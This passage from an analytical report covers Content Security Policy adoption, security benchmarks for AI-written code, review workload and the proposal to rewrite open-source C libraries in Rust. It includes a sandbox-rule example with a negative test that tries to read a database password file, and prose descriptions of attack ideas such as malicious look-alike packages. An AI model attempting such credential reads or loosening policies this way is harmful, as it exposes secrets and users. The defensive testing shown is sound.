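Even then, Dropbox's policy had a gap because it still contained 'unsafe-eval', which lets approved scripts run text as code, according to Dropbox's *CSP The Unexpected Eval*. Report URI's *Dropbox wrote down how they deployed CSP* shows that the current policy still contains it, although it now also has nonces and 'strict-dynamic'.

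### What stops other developers

*12 Angry Developers* (Roth, Gröber and colleagues, 2021) reports on a study in which 12 people with CSP experience described their work and then wrote a policy for a small note-taking application. Ten cited lack of time or money as a reason for weak or missing policies, along with lack of knowledge. The table groups the obstacles by type, with estimates of how much a coding agent could help.

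| Obstacle | What the study found | Could an agent remove it? |
|---|---|---|
| The site's own code | Eight developers ran into inline scripts and eight into inline event handlers | Mostly |
| Third-party scripts | Four said that outside services or libraries forced them to loosen the policy | Rarely |
| Browser differences | Eight complained of uneven support for CSP features | No, but browser makers have removed much of it |
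| Misunderstanding | Ten approved an outside supplier's whole domain, and none used a nonce for its script | Probably |
| Organization | Half said that security is often a secondary goal in development | No |

Agents are good at repetitive work like rewriting the site's own code. If an old site has 2,000 inline handlers and a programmer needs ten minutes to convert each one, the job would take about 333 hours and cost roughly $27,500 at the salary used for Bun. An agent could probably do most of it in a day or so for far less. But if the site then spent a month in report-only mode, as Dropbox did, the agent would not shorten that month much, because some problems appear only when real visitors use rare features.

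Third-party scripts are harder to fix because the site's owner can't edit them. *Web Execution Bundles* (2025) partly repeats an experiment by Steffens and colleagues, who found that 86% of sites couldn't adopt a policy that omits both 'unsafe-inline' and 'unsafe-eval', because JavaScript on their pages adds inline event handlers. If most of that JavaScript comes from advertisers and other suppliers, many sites would still break under such a policy even if an agent fixed all of their own code.

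Some of the broken features might not matter, and an agent could help a site's owner find a replacement for a chat box or a map. Replacing an advertising network is a business decision, though, because the site may depend on the advertising income. The network could use an agent to fix its script once for all its customers, but it has little reason to unless they insist.

Browser differences have become less important. *RETROCSP*'s compatibility table (Wilhelm, Roth and Stock), which covers browser versions from around early 2021, lists Safari as the only major browser without 'strict-dynamic'. Apple added it in 2022. Four years later, Helme found the keyword on only 2,774 sites, so Safari can't have been the main obstacle to strict policies.

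Developers misunderstand these policies partly because of the guides they read. Roth and colleagues found that popular guides gave examples that allow scripts from whole domains and didn't explain that a nonce can approve an outside script. Some of the developers started with tools that generate a policy automatically, but these also tended to allow scripts by domain. For inline scripts, the tools either added 'unsafe-inline' or left the site broken.

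An agent may know more about CSP than most web developers, but it may have learned from the same guides. If its goal is only to stop the error messages, the shortest solution is to add 'unsafe-inline', just as changing a type could silence a CHERI warning without fixing the program. The developer can set a better goal by putting a harmless test script in a review and requiring that the browser block the script while every button still works.

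Finally, a company has to decide that the protection is worth the risk of breaking its site. One developer warned that it is "very easy to break your site with CSP," for example by blocking a payment method that appears on only one page. A broken payment page loses sales immediately, while an attack the browser blocks usually goes unnoticed. Report URI found one public example of a blocked attack in Twitter's post. The researcher Masato Kinugawa reported in 2012 that CSP had stopped an XSS attack on Twitter's mobile site in Firefox.

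### Tools that convert a site automatically

Researchers were automating this work before coding agents existed. Early tools separated code from data in sites written in particular languages, such as PHP or ASP.NET. *EasyCSPeasy*, by Kaleli, Egele and Stringhini, describes a system that works with any language because it changes the finished page instead of the program that produces it.

EasyCSPeasy first explores a clean copy of the site and records every script it finds. A filter on the web server then checks each outgoing page. It allows the scripts recorded for that page, rewrites them where necessary, and removes or blocks the rest. The site's owner doesn't have to change the source code.

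The system also sends two policies at once, one with nonces and one with a list of approved addresses and hashes, and a script must satisfy both. This protects against some attacks that defeat an ordinary strict CSP. For example, an approved script may read an address from the page and load another script from that address. If an attacker can change the address, 'strict-dynamic' alone would let the attacker's script run, but the list blocks it.

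Kaleli and colleagues tested the system on six web applications, including WordPress, and commonly used features kept working. The generated policies also blocked known attacks on three vulnerable applications. However, the system has to explore a site again whenever the site's scripts change, and if it misses a page or a script that appears only after an unusual click, the policy may block legitimate code. A coding agent can read the source code as well as visit the pages, so it might find some of the scripts that exploration alone misses.

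Neither of the two recent surveys records whether people or AI wrote a site, so they can't show whether AI-built sites have stricter policies. They also give little sign that cheaper code has changed the web as a whole. Between 2024 and 2025, the share of sites with any policy rose from 18.5% to 21.9%, but HTTP Archive found hardly any change in the keywords that determine how strict a policy is. Coding agents have improved greatly since then, and the 2026 crawl used a different sample, so it is too early to rule out an effect from these agents.

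### Frameworks that set a policy by default

A web framework can remove much of the work without AI. It already generates a site's pages, so it can add a fresh nonce to each script and send the matching policy. One participant in *12 Angry Developers* wondered why frameworks that set other security headers automatically don't do the same for CSP.

Google followed this approach internally. By 2016, it had put strict policies on several large applications, including Photos and Cloud Console, and had released a browser extension that helped other developers look for incompatible code (Google, 2016). eWeek's *How Google Is Using Content Security Policy to Mitigate Web Flaws* reports that the company later built frameworks that set a policy without the developer noticing. CSP then covered more than 160 services and about 62% of Google's outgoing traffic. Google's engineers said that it had blocked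 more than 60% of XSS attempts in 2018.

Google's experience suggests that the work per site can be small once a central team has done the part common to all sites. But Google writes much of the code on its own pages and can tell its developers which framework to use. A small shop that depends on advertising and a dozen plug-ins has less control over the code on its pages.

Defaults can also fail if developers find them inconvenient. *12 Angry Developers* describes an experiment by Gorski and colleagues in which 30 students used a web framework to build a site with an embedded Google map. The results suggested that enforcing CSP by default did not make the students' sites more secure.

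But a default can spread very quickly when site owners don't have to do anything. Cloudflare, which delivers pages for more than a third of the sites in Helme's crawl, turns on network error reporting by default. The header that supports it appeared on 289,021 sites and pointed to Cloudflare on about 97% of them. Only 8,134 sites had set up reporting in their CSP.

Cloudflare could add that header without changing its customers' scripts, but a strict CSP on an old site would require changing them. A company that sells an AI website builder could add a strict CSP more easily, because it controls the template each new site starts from. If it put nonces in the template, its customers would get a strict policy without asking for one, at least until they added an advertisement or plug-in that didn't work with it.

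## Security flaws in code written by AI

An AI website builder could put a strict content security policy in its template once, but a model would still write most of the code on each new site. If that code has as many flaws per line as human code, and is so cheap that companies write three times as much, they will have three times as many new flaws. Those flaws could bring back some of the risk that strong protections remove.

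### An early experiment with students

*Lost at C* (Sandoval, Pearce and colleagues, 2022) studied AI-assisted code before coding agents existed. The researchers asked 58 students to complete a shopping-list program in C. Half the students got suggestions from an early OpenAI model, which they could accept, edit or ignore, and the rest worked without AI. Three researchers then read all the code together and marked the flaws.

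The AI made little difference to the rate of severe flaws. Students who used it had slightly fewer per line on average than students who didn't, and the researchers were reasonably confident that the AI group's rate was no more than 10% higher. About 63% of the flaws in the AI group's programs were in code the students had written themselves.

Functions that passed the basic tests still contained severe flaws, an average of 2.1 when written without AI and 2.2 when written with it. One student's function, for example, copied an item's name into a fixed-size string without checking the length.

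Today's agents write whole features, and the person in charge might write none of the code. The students' results are therefore weak evidence about current practice.

### Code that works but isn't secure

*BaxBench* (Vero, Mündler and colleagues, 2025) tested AI models on building the server side of web applications. Its 392 tasks combine 28 applications with different programming frameworks. The researchers checked whether each application worked and then attacked it. The best model, OpenAI's o1, produced working applications for 62% of the tasks. On average, the researchers could exploit about half of each model's working applications.

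Agents more often add features to existing software. Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *Is Vibe Coding Safe?*, built the SusVibes benchmark from 186 features in open-source Python projects. A human programmer had written each feature with a vulnerability that somebody later fixed. The researchers went back to the version before the fix, removed the feature and asked an agent to write it again. The request described what the feature should do but didn't mention security. The researchers used the project's own tests to see whether the new code worked. To see whether it was secure, they used tests from the original fix, which they had checked and sometimes revised.

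The best agent at the time, running on Claude 4 Sonnet, wrote working code for 57% of the tasks, but only 11.8% of its solutions were also secure. Endor Labs' *AI Coding Agent Security Benchmark* extends SusVibes and tests newer models. Endor Labs, which sells security tools for coding agents, tells each agent to follow security best practices but doesn't mention that the task involves a vulnerability. The September scores are from Haynes (2026), *Better models are making agent patch review more expensive, not less*.

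| Agent and model | Tested in 2026 | Working | Working and secure | Secure share of working code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, Opus 4.5 | February | 68.7% | 8.4% | 12% |
| Cursor, GPT-5.5 | April | 84.9% | 24.0% | 28% |
| Claude Code, Opus 5 | By September | 73.7% | 32.4% | 44% |
| Codex, GPT-6 Astra | By September | 82.1% | 34.1% | 42% |
| Claude Code, Fable 5.1 | By September | 87.2% | 37.4% | 43% |

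The secure share more than tripled in about seven months, but more than half of the best model's working solutions still had the flaw.

These scores don't show that AI writes less secure code than people do. Zhao and colleagues chose features that a human programmer had implemented insecurely, so the original programmers would have scored zero on security. The benchmark measures how well agents avoid mistakes that people are known to make, and ordinary features probably offer fewer chances to make them. Agents may remember a published fix from their training, which could raise their scores. Endor Labs excludes some tasks from the score for reasons like this and inspects how an agent arrived at its answer.

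Other tests have found a similar gap. In a study by Ilya Kabanov, four models from the first half of 2026 solved 83% to 95% of 200 tasks, but only 24% to 36% of their answers were both correct and free of the flaw the task was designed to expose. The security company Checkmarx paid for the study, though *AI coding models make working code, not secure code* (Lagonsin, 2026) says the company did not influence the conclusions.

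Veracode (2026), which sells security testing, reported in October that the models it tested passed 62% of its security tasks on average, and that Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Sol led with 73%. The prompts ask for ordinary code and give no security instructions. *AI-written code is getting safer, mostly where it was easy* (Vonk, 2026) breaks the results down by type of flaw. The models passed 87.4% of tasks on weak cryptography and 83.7% on database injection, but only 18% on cross-site scripting. A site written by AI may therefore need a strict content security policy more than a site written by hand.

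Memory-safe languages would not have prevented most of these flaws. The SusVibes tasks are in Python, and Veracode's are in Python, C#, JavaScript and Java, all of which already prevent ordinary memory errors. *SecureVibeBench* recreates 105 situations in which people introduced vulnerabilities into C and C++ code. Agents running on models such as Claude Sonnet 4.5 also struggled with these tasks.

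Benchmarks don't measure how many flaws reach users. Zhao and colleagues cite reports of exposed passwords for online services and broken login checks, some of which attackers exploited. These cases show that the problem is real, but not how common it is. No one seems to have reliably counted the vulnerabilities traced to AI-written code and compared that count with the number in human code.

### Why a rule that allows too much passes every test

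It is easy to write sandbox rules and security policies that allow too much, and ordinary tests can't detect this mistake because the program still works. When a rule blocks something the program needs, a test fails and somebody fixes the rule.

Suppose a shop has a service that sends customers their invoices. The invoices are in one folder, and the database password is in another folder nearby. A developer asks an agent to sandbox the service, and the agent could write either of these rules, where "**" means everything in the folder and its subfolders:

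```
Narrow:  allow read /srv/shop/invoices/**
Broad:   allow read /srv/shop/**
```

An ordinary test checks that the service can open an invoice. A negative test checks that it can't open something it has no business reading. Both of these run inside the sandbox:

```python
def test_opens_invoice():
    with open("/srv/shop/invoices/1042.pdf", "rb") as f:
        assert f.read()

def test_cannot_open_password():
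    with pytest.raises(PermissionError):
        open("/srv/shop/config/db-password")
```

| Test | Narrow rule | Broad rule |
|---|---|---|
| Opens an invoice | Passes | Passes |
| Cannot open the password | Passes | Fails |

Without the negative test, an agent has a reason to prefer the broad rule. Suppose it starts with the narrow one, and the service then fails because it also needs the shop's logo from an images folder. The right fix is to allow that one file, but allowing the whole shop folder also works and prevents similar failures later. Ordinary tests won't reveal that the new rule is too broad, because removing a restriction almost never stops a program from working.

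The same point holds for any set of permissions. Let *A* be everything the rule allows, *N* everything the program needs during its ordinary tests, and *F* everything the negative tests try to reach. The ordinary tests pass if *N* ⊆ *A*, so they can detect a rule that allows too little but not one that allows too much. The negative tests pass if *A* ∩ *F* = ∅, so they detect a rule that allows anything in *F*.

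Negative tests have limits as well. This one would miss a rule that exposed a folder of customer records, because it checks only whether the service can read the password file. It could also pass with no sandbox at all if the operating system's ordinary file permissions already kept the service from reading the password. To rule this out, the developer should run the test once with the sandbox switched off and confirm that it fails.

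No one seems to have measured how often coding agents write rules that are too broad. The ChatGPT user in Alhindi and Hallett's study first got sandbox rules that allowed everything, but that was a single case.

Ordinary code can have the same problem. Haynes describes a task based on a flaw in the compiler for Vyper, a language for smart contracts. The code that the compiler generates to copy an array must copy the data before it changes the array's stored length. Otherwise, a bounds check can pass when it should fail. If a programmer reversed the order, the project's functional tests would all still pass.

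### Tests that repeat the author's mistake

AI coding agents write many tests. Microsoft's .NET team let GitHub's Copilot agent work on the core of .NET, a widely used software platform, for ten months from May 2025. Test code made up 65.7% of the lines the agent added, compared with 49.9% in a sample of changes by people, partly because the team often assigned it test-writing.

These tests are weaker evidence if the agent misunderstood the task. Suppose the shop wants customers to see only their own invoices, but the agent interprets the task as letting any logged-in customer open any invoice. It writes code that checks only the login, and a test in which a logged-in customer opens invoice 1042. The test passes even if that invoice belongs to another customer.

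If different authors write the code and the tests, the second might not repeat the first's mistake. Suppose each misreads 10% of requirements, independently of the other. Both will then misread about 1% of them. If one model writes both the code and the tests in one session, the share misread in both could be close to 10%. These percentages are invented for illustration, because nobody seems to have measured how often an agent's tests repeat its mistakes.

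An agent can also change the existing tests to match its code. The .NET team asked Copilot to make the platform's text-search feature reject certain patterns that it had always accepted. The agent made the change and updated the tests that now failed. The engineer who reviewed the work noticed that those tests recorded a deliberate decision, and closed both the change and the request behind it. An engineer who checked only whether the tests passed would probably have approved the mistake.

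### Packages that don't exist

Most programs use packages that other people have published, and a language model sometimes recommends one that doesn't exist. Spracklen and colleagues, quoted in OpenSSF (2025), explain that an attacker can exploit this by publishing a malicious package under the invented name.

When a model's code names a package that doesn't exist, the mistake is fairly harmless until an attacker publishes one under that name. Before then, the installation fails and the agent looks for something else. Afterward, the installation succeeds. If the attacker's package also does what the code needs, perhaps because the attacker copied a real one, the program passes its tests. An attacker can look for useful names by giving popular models thousands of ordinary programming requests and recording the nonexistent packages in their answers.

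Rust doesn't stop a malicious package from stealing data, because the package can do so without any memory error. A sandbox can limit the damage, but only if the package runs inside it, and some packages run code on the developer's own computer during installation.

OpenSSF, a foundation for open-source security, advises developers to tell their coding assistant to prefer popular packages and avoid adding any that may be malicious or invented. This depends on the model detecting its own mistakes. A company gets stronger protection by keeping a list of approved packages and having its build system block all others. Someone then has to review each addition to the list, and agents can make the list grow very quickly.

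### More code than people can review

*AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) followed 802 developers at a software company that set out to double its output with AI. The company measured output in pull requests, which are proposed code changes that a colleague normally reviews before they are merged. Each active developer made about 21 a month in early 2025 and 44 in April 2026. AI was probably not the only cause, and He, Agarwal and colleagues estimate that it raised output to between 1.5 and 2.1 times the earlier level.

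| | Before | By April 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Pull requests across the company | 1 | 3.1 times as many |
| People reviewing them | 1 | 1.5 times as many |
| Share that a person reviewed | 89% | 68% |
| Share on which a reviewer wrote a comment | About 39% | About 21% |
| Share that an AI tool reviewed | About 19% | About 84% |

The share of changes that no person reviewed rose from 11% to 32% while the total number of changes tripled, so about nine times as many changes now go without human review. People also reviewed more changes than before, but most of the extra reviews were approvals without a comment.

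This company was unusually keen on AI. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) examined 224 organizations that work on AI and found a smaller difference. People reviewed about 80% of pull requests that showed no sign of AI, and typically about 8 percentage points fewer of those that did. The gap disappeared once the analysis weighted the results by contributor. For people who run fleets of agents, however, the review rate fell from about 50% in early 2024, when they were already getting less review than others, to below 30%.

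The .NET team kept tighter control by letting only maintainers ask the agent for changes. By March 2026, maintainers had requested 878 changes and merged 535. They had rejected or abandoned 253, and the rest were still open. Of the changes they had decided on, they merged 68% of the agent's and 87% of those by Microsoft's developers. The comparison isn't entirely fair, because the agent and the developers got different kinds of work.

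Starting such work takes very little effort. One engineer assigned the agent more than 20 tasks by phone during a child's birthday party and had reviewed 22 pull requests by that evening. One fix, which might have taken hours to find, took five minutes to review. But security review can be much slower. Sandoval and colleagues spent 66 person-hours reviewing the students' short programs, about an hour for every 250 lines.

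Haynes compares the cost of generating code with Fable 5.1 to the cost of reviewing it. The model's fees for the whole benchmark were $672, and it produced 156 working solutions, of which 67 were secure. Identifying those 67 requires checking all 156, which would cost $7,800 at half an hour each and $100 an hour. Each secure solution would cost about $126, including only $10 in model fees, so eliminating the fees would reduce the total by only 8%. The estimate assumes that half an hour is enough to find the flaw.

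### What a low revert rate shows about security

The .NET team reverted, or took back out of the program, three of the agent's 535 merged changes (0.6%) and 33 of 4,251 others (0.8%). At the company He and colleagues studied, output doubled while the share of changes that developers reverted stayed about the same or fell slightly.

These rates are good evidence that the agents' code did not often break things in obvious ways. A change that stops customers from logging in will usually produce complaints within hours, and reverting it is the quickest remedy. He and colleagues found no sudden drop in quality but say they can't rule out hidden drawbacks. The .NET figure is also uncertain because it is based on only three reverts. The true rate could be anywhere from about 0.1% to 1.6%, or up to twice the rate for other changes.

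A revert rate shows much less about security, because developers revert a change only after noticing something wrong. Nobody would complain about the broad file rule until somebody stole the password. Even when a team finds a vulnerability, it will often add a fix and keep the rest of the change, so the revert rate doesn't include the flaw.

The .NET team also counted its agent changes early, when most were less than three months old. If the average flaw lasts 2.5 years, as Google estimates for memory errors, people find only about 10% of flaws in the first three months. A company could get a better measure by labeling AI-written changes, as the company in He and colleagues' study does, and counting the vulnerabilities that researchers or attackers find in them over several years.

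### Do security instructions help?

Asking the AI assistant for secure code is the cheapest remedy, and OpenSSF publishes sample instructions that developers can adapt. They tell the assistant to limit permissions to what the program needs, write negative tests and send a content security policy with web pages. OpenSSF bases them on expert opinion and published research and invites others to test them. It warns that irrelevant instructions can make the code worse, and it doesn't recommend telling a model to act as a security expert, because some experiments found that this worsened the results.

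Measured effects vary a lot. Zhao and colleagues told agents exactly which type of flaw to avoid. According to Zhao's conference slides, security improved by only about 3 percentage points, while the share of working solutions fell by as much as 7 points. Newer models may follow such hints better.

*Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* (2026) reports a more encouraging trial on BaxBench's 28 applications. The model received detailed security requirements for its task from a database.

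| Result in one run | No security instructions | With security requirements |
|---|---|---|
| Working applications | 26 | 21 |
| Working and secure | 17 | 18 |
| Working but insecure | 9 | 3 |

Adding the requirements produced only one more secure application, but six fewer that worked and were open to attack. That reduction is valuable because a developer will notice an application that doesn't work, but may release a vulnerable one that does. The numbers are small, and someone would still have to repair the seven that failed.

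### Rules that a compiler or build system enforces

Developers can add a single line to a Rust package that makes the compiler reject any unsafe block in it, whoever wrote the code. This is more reliable than instructing an AI agent to avoid unsafe code, which may or may not work. An agent could delete the line, so the build system should check that it is still there.

For memory flaws, the choice of programming language matters far more than how much code a company writes. By a cautious estimate, Android's Rust has about 800 times fewer memory flaws per line than its C and C++. At that rate, a company could write 100 times as much code in Rust and have about an eighth as many memory flaws. But people wrote most of Android's Rust, and AI-written Rust with thousands of unsafe blocks, like Bun's, may have more flaws per line.

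A build system can enforce other rules in the same way. It can refuse unapproved packages, reject a content security policy that contains 'unsafe-inline' without a nonce, and run the negative tests on every change. The agent that writes a change should not be able to edit these checks, and a person should approve any change to them. A reviewer would then have a few dozen lines to read carefully instead of thousands. These checks still won't catch the mistake with other customers' invoices unless somebody thinks to write a test for it.

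### Independent reviewers and scanners

A reviewer who didn't write the code can question the assumptions behind it, as the .NET engineer did. AI reviewers are much cheaper than people, and the evidence for them is strongest when they look for a specific mistake. Before Bun's merge, agents searching for one particular error in its use of references confirmed 23 cases that the tests had missed. A general request to review a change gives the model less guidance. The flat revert rate at He and colleagues' company doesn't show that its AI reviewers catch security flaws, for the same reasons it doesn't show that the code is secure.

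Using another company's model to review the code may help less than hoped. Fable 5.1 and GPT-6 Astra left almost the same share of their working solutions insecure, and Haynes suspects that the difficulty comes from the problem itself rather than from either model. The overall scores don't show whether both models fail on the same tasks, but if they do, one may also overlook the other's flaws.

Scanners search code for known dangerous patterns and can check every change for almost nothing, but they make many mistakes. Sandoval and colleagues decided against CodeQL, a widely used scanner, and read the code themselves because CodeQL raised too many false alarms and missed too many real flaws. In the SafeTrans study, scanners also missed two kinds of flaw that survived translation into Rust.

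Trying an attack shows more clearly than a scanner's warning whether code has a flaw. *Detect–Repair–Verify for LLM-Generated Code* (2026) therefore includes functional tests and exploit tests for each program in its benchmark. The exploit tests send malicious input to check whether a flaw is still there. A company can likewise keep a test for each of its own past vulnerabilities and run it whenever an agent changes the code. These tests cost little to run, but they protect only against attacks that somebody has already thought of.

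## The Great Refactor: a proposal to rewrite 100 million lines

In August 2025, IFP published *The Great Refactor*, in which Herbie Bradley and Girish Sastry propose rewriting 100 million lines of open-source code in Rust before 2030, for about $100 million. They think software lacks memory safety mainly because the labor costs too much, and they expect AI to do most of the translation. Several teams have since tried rewriting real programs with AI, so the proposal's figures can now be checked against their results.

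### What the $100 million would buy

A new nonprofit with 43 staff would do the work over three to five years. It would look for libraries that much other software depends on, that have few maintainers, and that have enough tests to check a translation. One of IFP's examples of a library with too few maintainers is Dnsmasq, a network program found in home routers and most versions of Linux. It had one main maintainer in 2017, when researchers found several buffer overflows in it. Neglected libraries with good tests may be scarce, though, because writing tests takes time that their maintainers don't have.

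The nonprofit would start with system utilities and with code that reads files and network messages. The second group is probably the better target. Wallach says hand-written parsers, which read complex data formats, are arguably the source of 80% of known vulnerabilities in C and C++ programs.

To check the translations, the staff would build a system that goes beyond ordinary tests and fuzzing. Experts in Rust and security would then review the code. The table shows IFP's budget, regrouped and converted to a cost per line for 100 million lines.

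| Item | Cost over five years | Per line |
|---|---|---|
| 15 Rust engineers to validate translations | $21.0 million | 21¢ |
| 28 other staff | $48.9 million | 49¢ |
| AI model fees | $5.0 million | 5¢ |
| Grants to maintainers | $10.0 million | 10¢ |
| Outside attack testing and bug bounties | $5.0 million | 5¢ |
| Rent, insurance, travel and other overheads | $8.3 million | 8¢ |
| Total | $98.2 million | 98¢ |

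IFP concedes four main risks. Attackers will turn to other weaknesses, such as tricking employees. Even extensive tests may not show that a translation behaves like the original. Many organizations are slow to install new versions, and many maintainers don't know Rust.

### Has anyone funded it?

Nobody appears to have provided the $100 million. The Institute for Progress reports that it and other philanthropic funders gave Bradley grants "to explore founding a nonprofit" with a similar aim. It reported this in a call for new proposals, which its *IFP Update* (2026) announced in January. Since then, no one seems to have publicly announced a working organization or a first translated library.

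Other funders have committed much smaller sums to memory safety. Weber-Mendez and Gran (2026), in *Four Years of Momentum*, announced a $100,000 grant for 2026 to the nonprofit behind Prossimo, which promotes memory-safe software. Canonical is funding a PhD at the University of Bristol on translating C to Rust for Ubuntu's security tools, as Daws (2026) reports in *Canonical backs Bristol PhD to automate C to Rust translation*. The UK's public research funder is matching Canonical's money for the three-year project, according to Slashdot's *Canonical is Funding a PhD to Automate C to Rust Translation* (2026). DARPA has spent more on TRACTOR, but that program develops translation tools rather than replacing the libraries people use.

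### Where the $2 billion in savings comes from

IFP estimates that the project would save about $2 billion. It assumes that attackers exploit 0.5% of vulnerabilities, that each exploited one costs $4.8 million, and that fixing a vulnerability costs $3,000. The expected cost of one flaw is therefore

0.005 × $4,800,000 + $3,000 = $27,000

IFP doesn't say how many flaws it expects to remove, but $2 billion divided by $27,000 is about 74,000. IFP also assumes that 70% of vulnerabilities are memory errors, which implies that the 100 million lines would contain about 106,000 flaws of all kinds, or roughly one per 1,000 lines.

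The figure is reasonable for new C code, since Google estimates about one memory flaw per 1,000 lines in Android's C and C++. But many of the libraries IFP has in mind are decades old, and people have already found and fixed many of their flaws. Under the assumptions used earlier for Android, ten-year-old code would have between 18 and 87 memory flaws per million lines, or about 67 if some of its flaws were especially hard to find.

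The share of flaws that are exploited may also be higher than 0.5%. The security company VulnCheck puts it near 1.4% for 2026, according to Clubic's *Twice as many security flaws recorded in 2026 as in 2025*. That would raise the expected cost of a flaw to $70,200.

| Memory flaws per million lines | Saved if attackers exploit 0.5% | Saved if attackers exploit 1.4% |
|---|---|---|
| 740 (implied by IFP's total) | $2.0 billion | $5.2 billion |
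| 87 (slow aging) | $235 million | $611 million |
| 67 (fast aging, with some hidden flaws) | $181 million | $470 million |
| 18 (fast aging) | $49 million | $126 million |

The savings exceed the budget in every case except the lowest. But every case assumes that all users switch to the Rust version. On IFP's figures, the project would break even if the new libraries replaced 5% of the use of the old ones. With 87 flaws per million lines and 0.5% exploited, they would have to replace 42% for the project to break even.

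The calculation also leaves out any new flaws in the translations, such as the 113 issues that auditors found in Ubuntu's Rust tools. But it may greatly understate the damage from a flaw in a popular library, because attackers can use it against many organizations. IFP cites an estimate that Heartbleed cost at least $500 million, as much as 104 incidents at $4.8 million each. Preventing a few flaws like that could account for most of the savings, so the choice of libraries matters more than the number of lines.

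### Is a dollar a line enough?

The budget allows 5 cents per line for AI models. Reboot's translations cost 8.2 cents per line and Bun's cost 31 cents, or $8.2 million and $31 million for 100 million lines. The AI company Asari AI paid less, translating four C libraries with more than 40,000 lines in total for $50 to $500 each, according to SoftwareSeni's *AI assisted code translation from C to Rust*. That is at most about 5 cents per line. IFP's figure was therefore a good guess for 2025, and even at Bun's rate the fees would use less than a third of the total budget.

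Checking is more likely to exceed its budget. If the 15 Rust engineers spent five years only reading code, at 400 lines an hour for 2,000 hours a year each, they would read 60 million of the 100 million lines.

Tests could replace much of the reading, but they have to be prepared first. Reboot's developers spent 10 to 20 hours preparing held-out tests for each program, and the programs averaged about 12,000 lines. At that rate, tests for 100 million lines would take 42 to 84 person-years, while the budget provides 75 person-years of Rust engineers for the whole project. Agents could do more of this preparation today.

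IFP expected this problem. Although it bases its proposal on labor being the main bottleneck, it also says that human review now takes more time than translation. It therefore doesn't assume that making code cheaper to write removes the need for skilled labor.

### Microsoft's goal of a million lines a month

In December 2025, Galen Hunt, a senior engineer at Microsoft, announced a more ambitious goal in a LinkedIn job advertisement. He wanted "to eliminate every line of C and C++ from Microsoft by 2030" by combining AI with conventional algorithms. The target was "1 engineer, 1 month, 1 million lines of code."

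Four days later, after the post had drawn wide attention, Hunt added that Microsoft was not rewriting Windows in Rust with AI. Hunt described the team's work as research into tools for moving code between languages, and said that Rust wasn't necessarily the final choice. Microsoft's head of communications also denied any plan to rewrite Windows 11 with AI, according to Windows Latest's *Microsoft denies rewriting Windows 11 using AI* (2025). The edited post still included the target of a million lines a month.

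Van Deursen, in *Migrating Legacy Like a North Star Engineer*, calls it "dangerously naive" to suggest that AI will let a few engineers modernize millions of lines in months. Van Deursen worries less about Microsoft, which probably has good tests already, than about governments and banks that might neglect their old systems while they wait for such an engineer to appear. They should instead start preparing now:

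- Separate the system into parts that they can replace one at a time.
- Find out how the software is supposed to behave.
- Make the code more uniform.
- Write more tests, using the old system to supply the right answers.
- Arrange to run the old and new versions side by side and compare them.

None of these steps translates any code, and each takes a substantial investment.

Five months after Hunt's post, Bun exceeded the target. One engineer supervised the translation of 535,496 lines in eleven days, a pace of almost 1.5 million lines a month. Measured up to the stable release, fourteen weeks after the merge, the pace was about 150,000 lines a month, and by then other developers were helping. Bun met several of Van Deursen's conditions before the work began. It had more than 60,000 tests, and Sumner knew how the program should behave.

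At Hunt's pace, the five AI engineers in IFP's budget could translate 100 million lines in 20 months. But most of the target libraries would be less well prepared than Bun, and the engineers wouldn't know them as well as Sumner knew Bun.

### Do maintainers have time for a rewrite?

A translated library needs someone to maintain it. The best candidates are usually the people who maintain the C version, but many of them already have more work than they can handle. Anthropic's Project Glasswing, which began in April 2026 and uses AI to look for vulnerabilities in important software, gives some idea of their workload. Anthropic keeps a public ledger of what the project finds in open-source code.

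| | Early September 2026 | Early November 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Possible flaws found | 26,153 | 37,966 |
| Reported to maintainers and not marked fixed | 2,096 | 4,866 |
| Marked fixed | 202 | 217 |

The September figures come from Garrity's *The Anthropic Glasswing Receipts Are Starting to Trickle In* (2026). The November figures come from VulnCheck's *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026) and Poireault's *Anthropic's Glasswing Finds Many Security Flaws Yet Delivers Few Fixes* (2026).

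Most of the findings never reached maintainers, so maintainers have not ignored 99% of them. Anthropic's *Launching an opt-in vulnerability-finding service for open-source software* (2026) reports that the company's staff had reviewed only about 6,000 of the 29,000 candidates it had by October. Cornelißen (2026), in *Glasswing*, compared VulnCheck's criticism with Anthropic's figures and concluded that part of the criticism rests on a misreading. Cornelißen also points out that the ledger omits flaws that companies such as Microsoft and Cisco find in their own products and fix quietly.

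A fairer comparison counts only the flaws maintainers know about, of which they have fixed about 4%. Many of the reports are recent, and the ledger can be out of date. According to Garrity, it was not updated from May until early September. Even so, the number of open reports more than doubled in two months, while the ledger gained only 15 fixes.

Some reported flaws also turn out not to be vulnerabilities. Curl's developers rejected 19 of the 34 published reports they received from Anthropic's scanner, according to VulnCheck, and they had to examine each one to decide.

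AI can write the fixes too, but not yet well enough to relieve maintainers of the work. In *Frontier Models' Vulnerability Patches are Often F.L.A.W.E.D*, Mierczuk, Michaels and Hoodlet asked ChatGPT 5.5 and Claude Opus 4.8 to fix six serious and complex vulnerabilities under a range of conditions. The models rarely closed every route to the flaw without changing how the program behaved. Some patches passed the tests but left the underlying cause in place. Newer models may do better, and six difficult cases are weak evidence of how well models handle routine fixes.

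A maintainer who doesn't have time to check a ten-line fix probably won't have time to check a rewrite of the whole library. But the backlog also strengthens the case for rewriting, because a good Rust version would save the maintainer from handling most memory errors one by one.

IFP's $10 million for maintainers is small for a project of this size. If the average library had 20,000 lines, the project would cover 5,000 libraries, and the grants would average $2,000 per library over five years. IFP plans to give grants to only some libraries. If it chose a tenth of them, each could receive $20,000, which might pay for a couple of months of a maintainer's time but not for years of upkeep.

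The nonprofit could maintain the new libraries itself, but only until it closes. If one person can maintain 100,000 lines, it will take 1,000 people to maintain 100 million. Agents could reduce that number, but a maintainer who doesn't know Rust will struggle to judge the changes an agent proposes.

In June 2026, the Linux Foundation (2026) announced Akrites, a shared team that will fix and disclose vulnerabilities in critical open-source software. Its founding members have promised engineers as well as money.

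### Getting users to switch

Even a well-maintained Rust library doesn't protect a program that still uses the C version. Intel's *IDEAS for TRACTOR* notes that translating C into safe Rust usually changes the interface that other programs call. Developers of those programs must then change their code or, as with giflib, call the library through a compatibility layer, which often needs unsafe blocks.

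Switching can also take a long time. Ubuntu took about 19 months to adopt one set of tools that already existed. IFP budgets for five people to encourage adoption of all the new libraries. They could save effort by focusing on the major Linux distributions, which choose the libraries that millions of machines install.

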